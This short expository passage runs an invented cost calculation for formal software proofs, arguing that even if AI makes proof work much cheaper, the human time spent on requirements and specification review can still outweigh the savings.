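For ordinary software, whether a proof is worth its cost depends on how far the total cost can fall. In the invented case where each fault costs 20,000 euros, the yearly cost of the proof would have to drop by about 90%, from 27,000 euros to below 2,800. If property tests already catch 60% of the faults, it would have to fall below 1,120. AI could plausibly reduce the cost of writing and repairing proofs by that much. But if deciding on requirements and reviewing specifications still takes 3,000 euros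 of people's time a year, the proof would cost more than it saves even if the AI's work were free.
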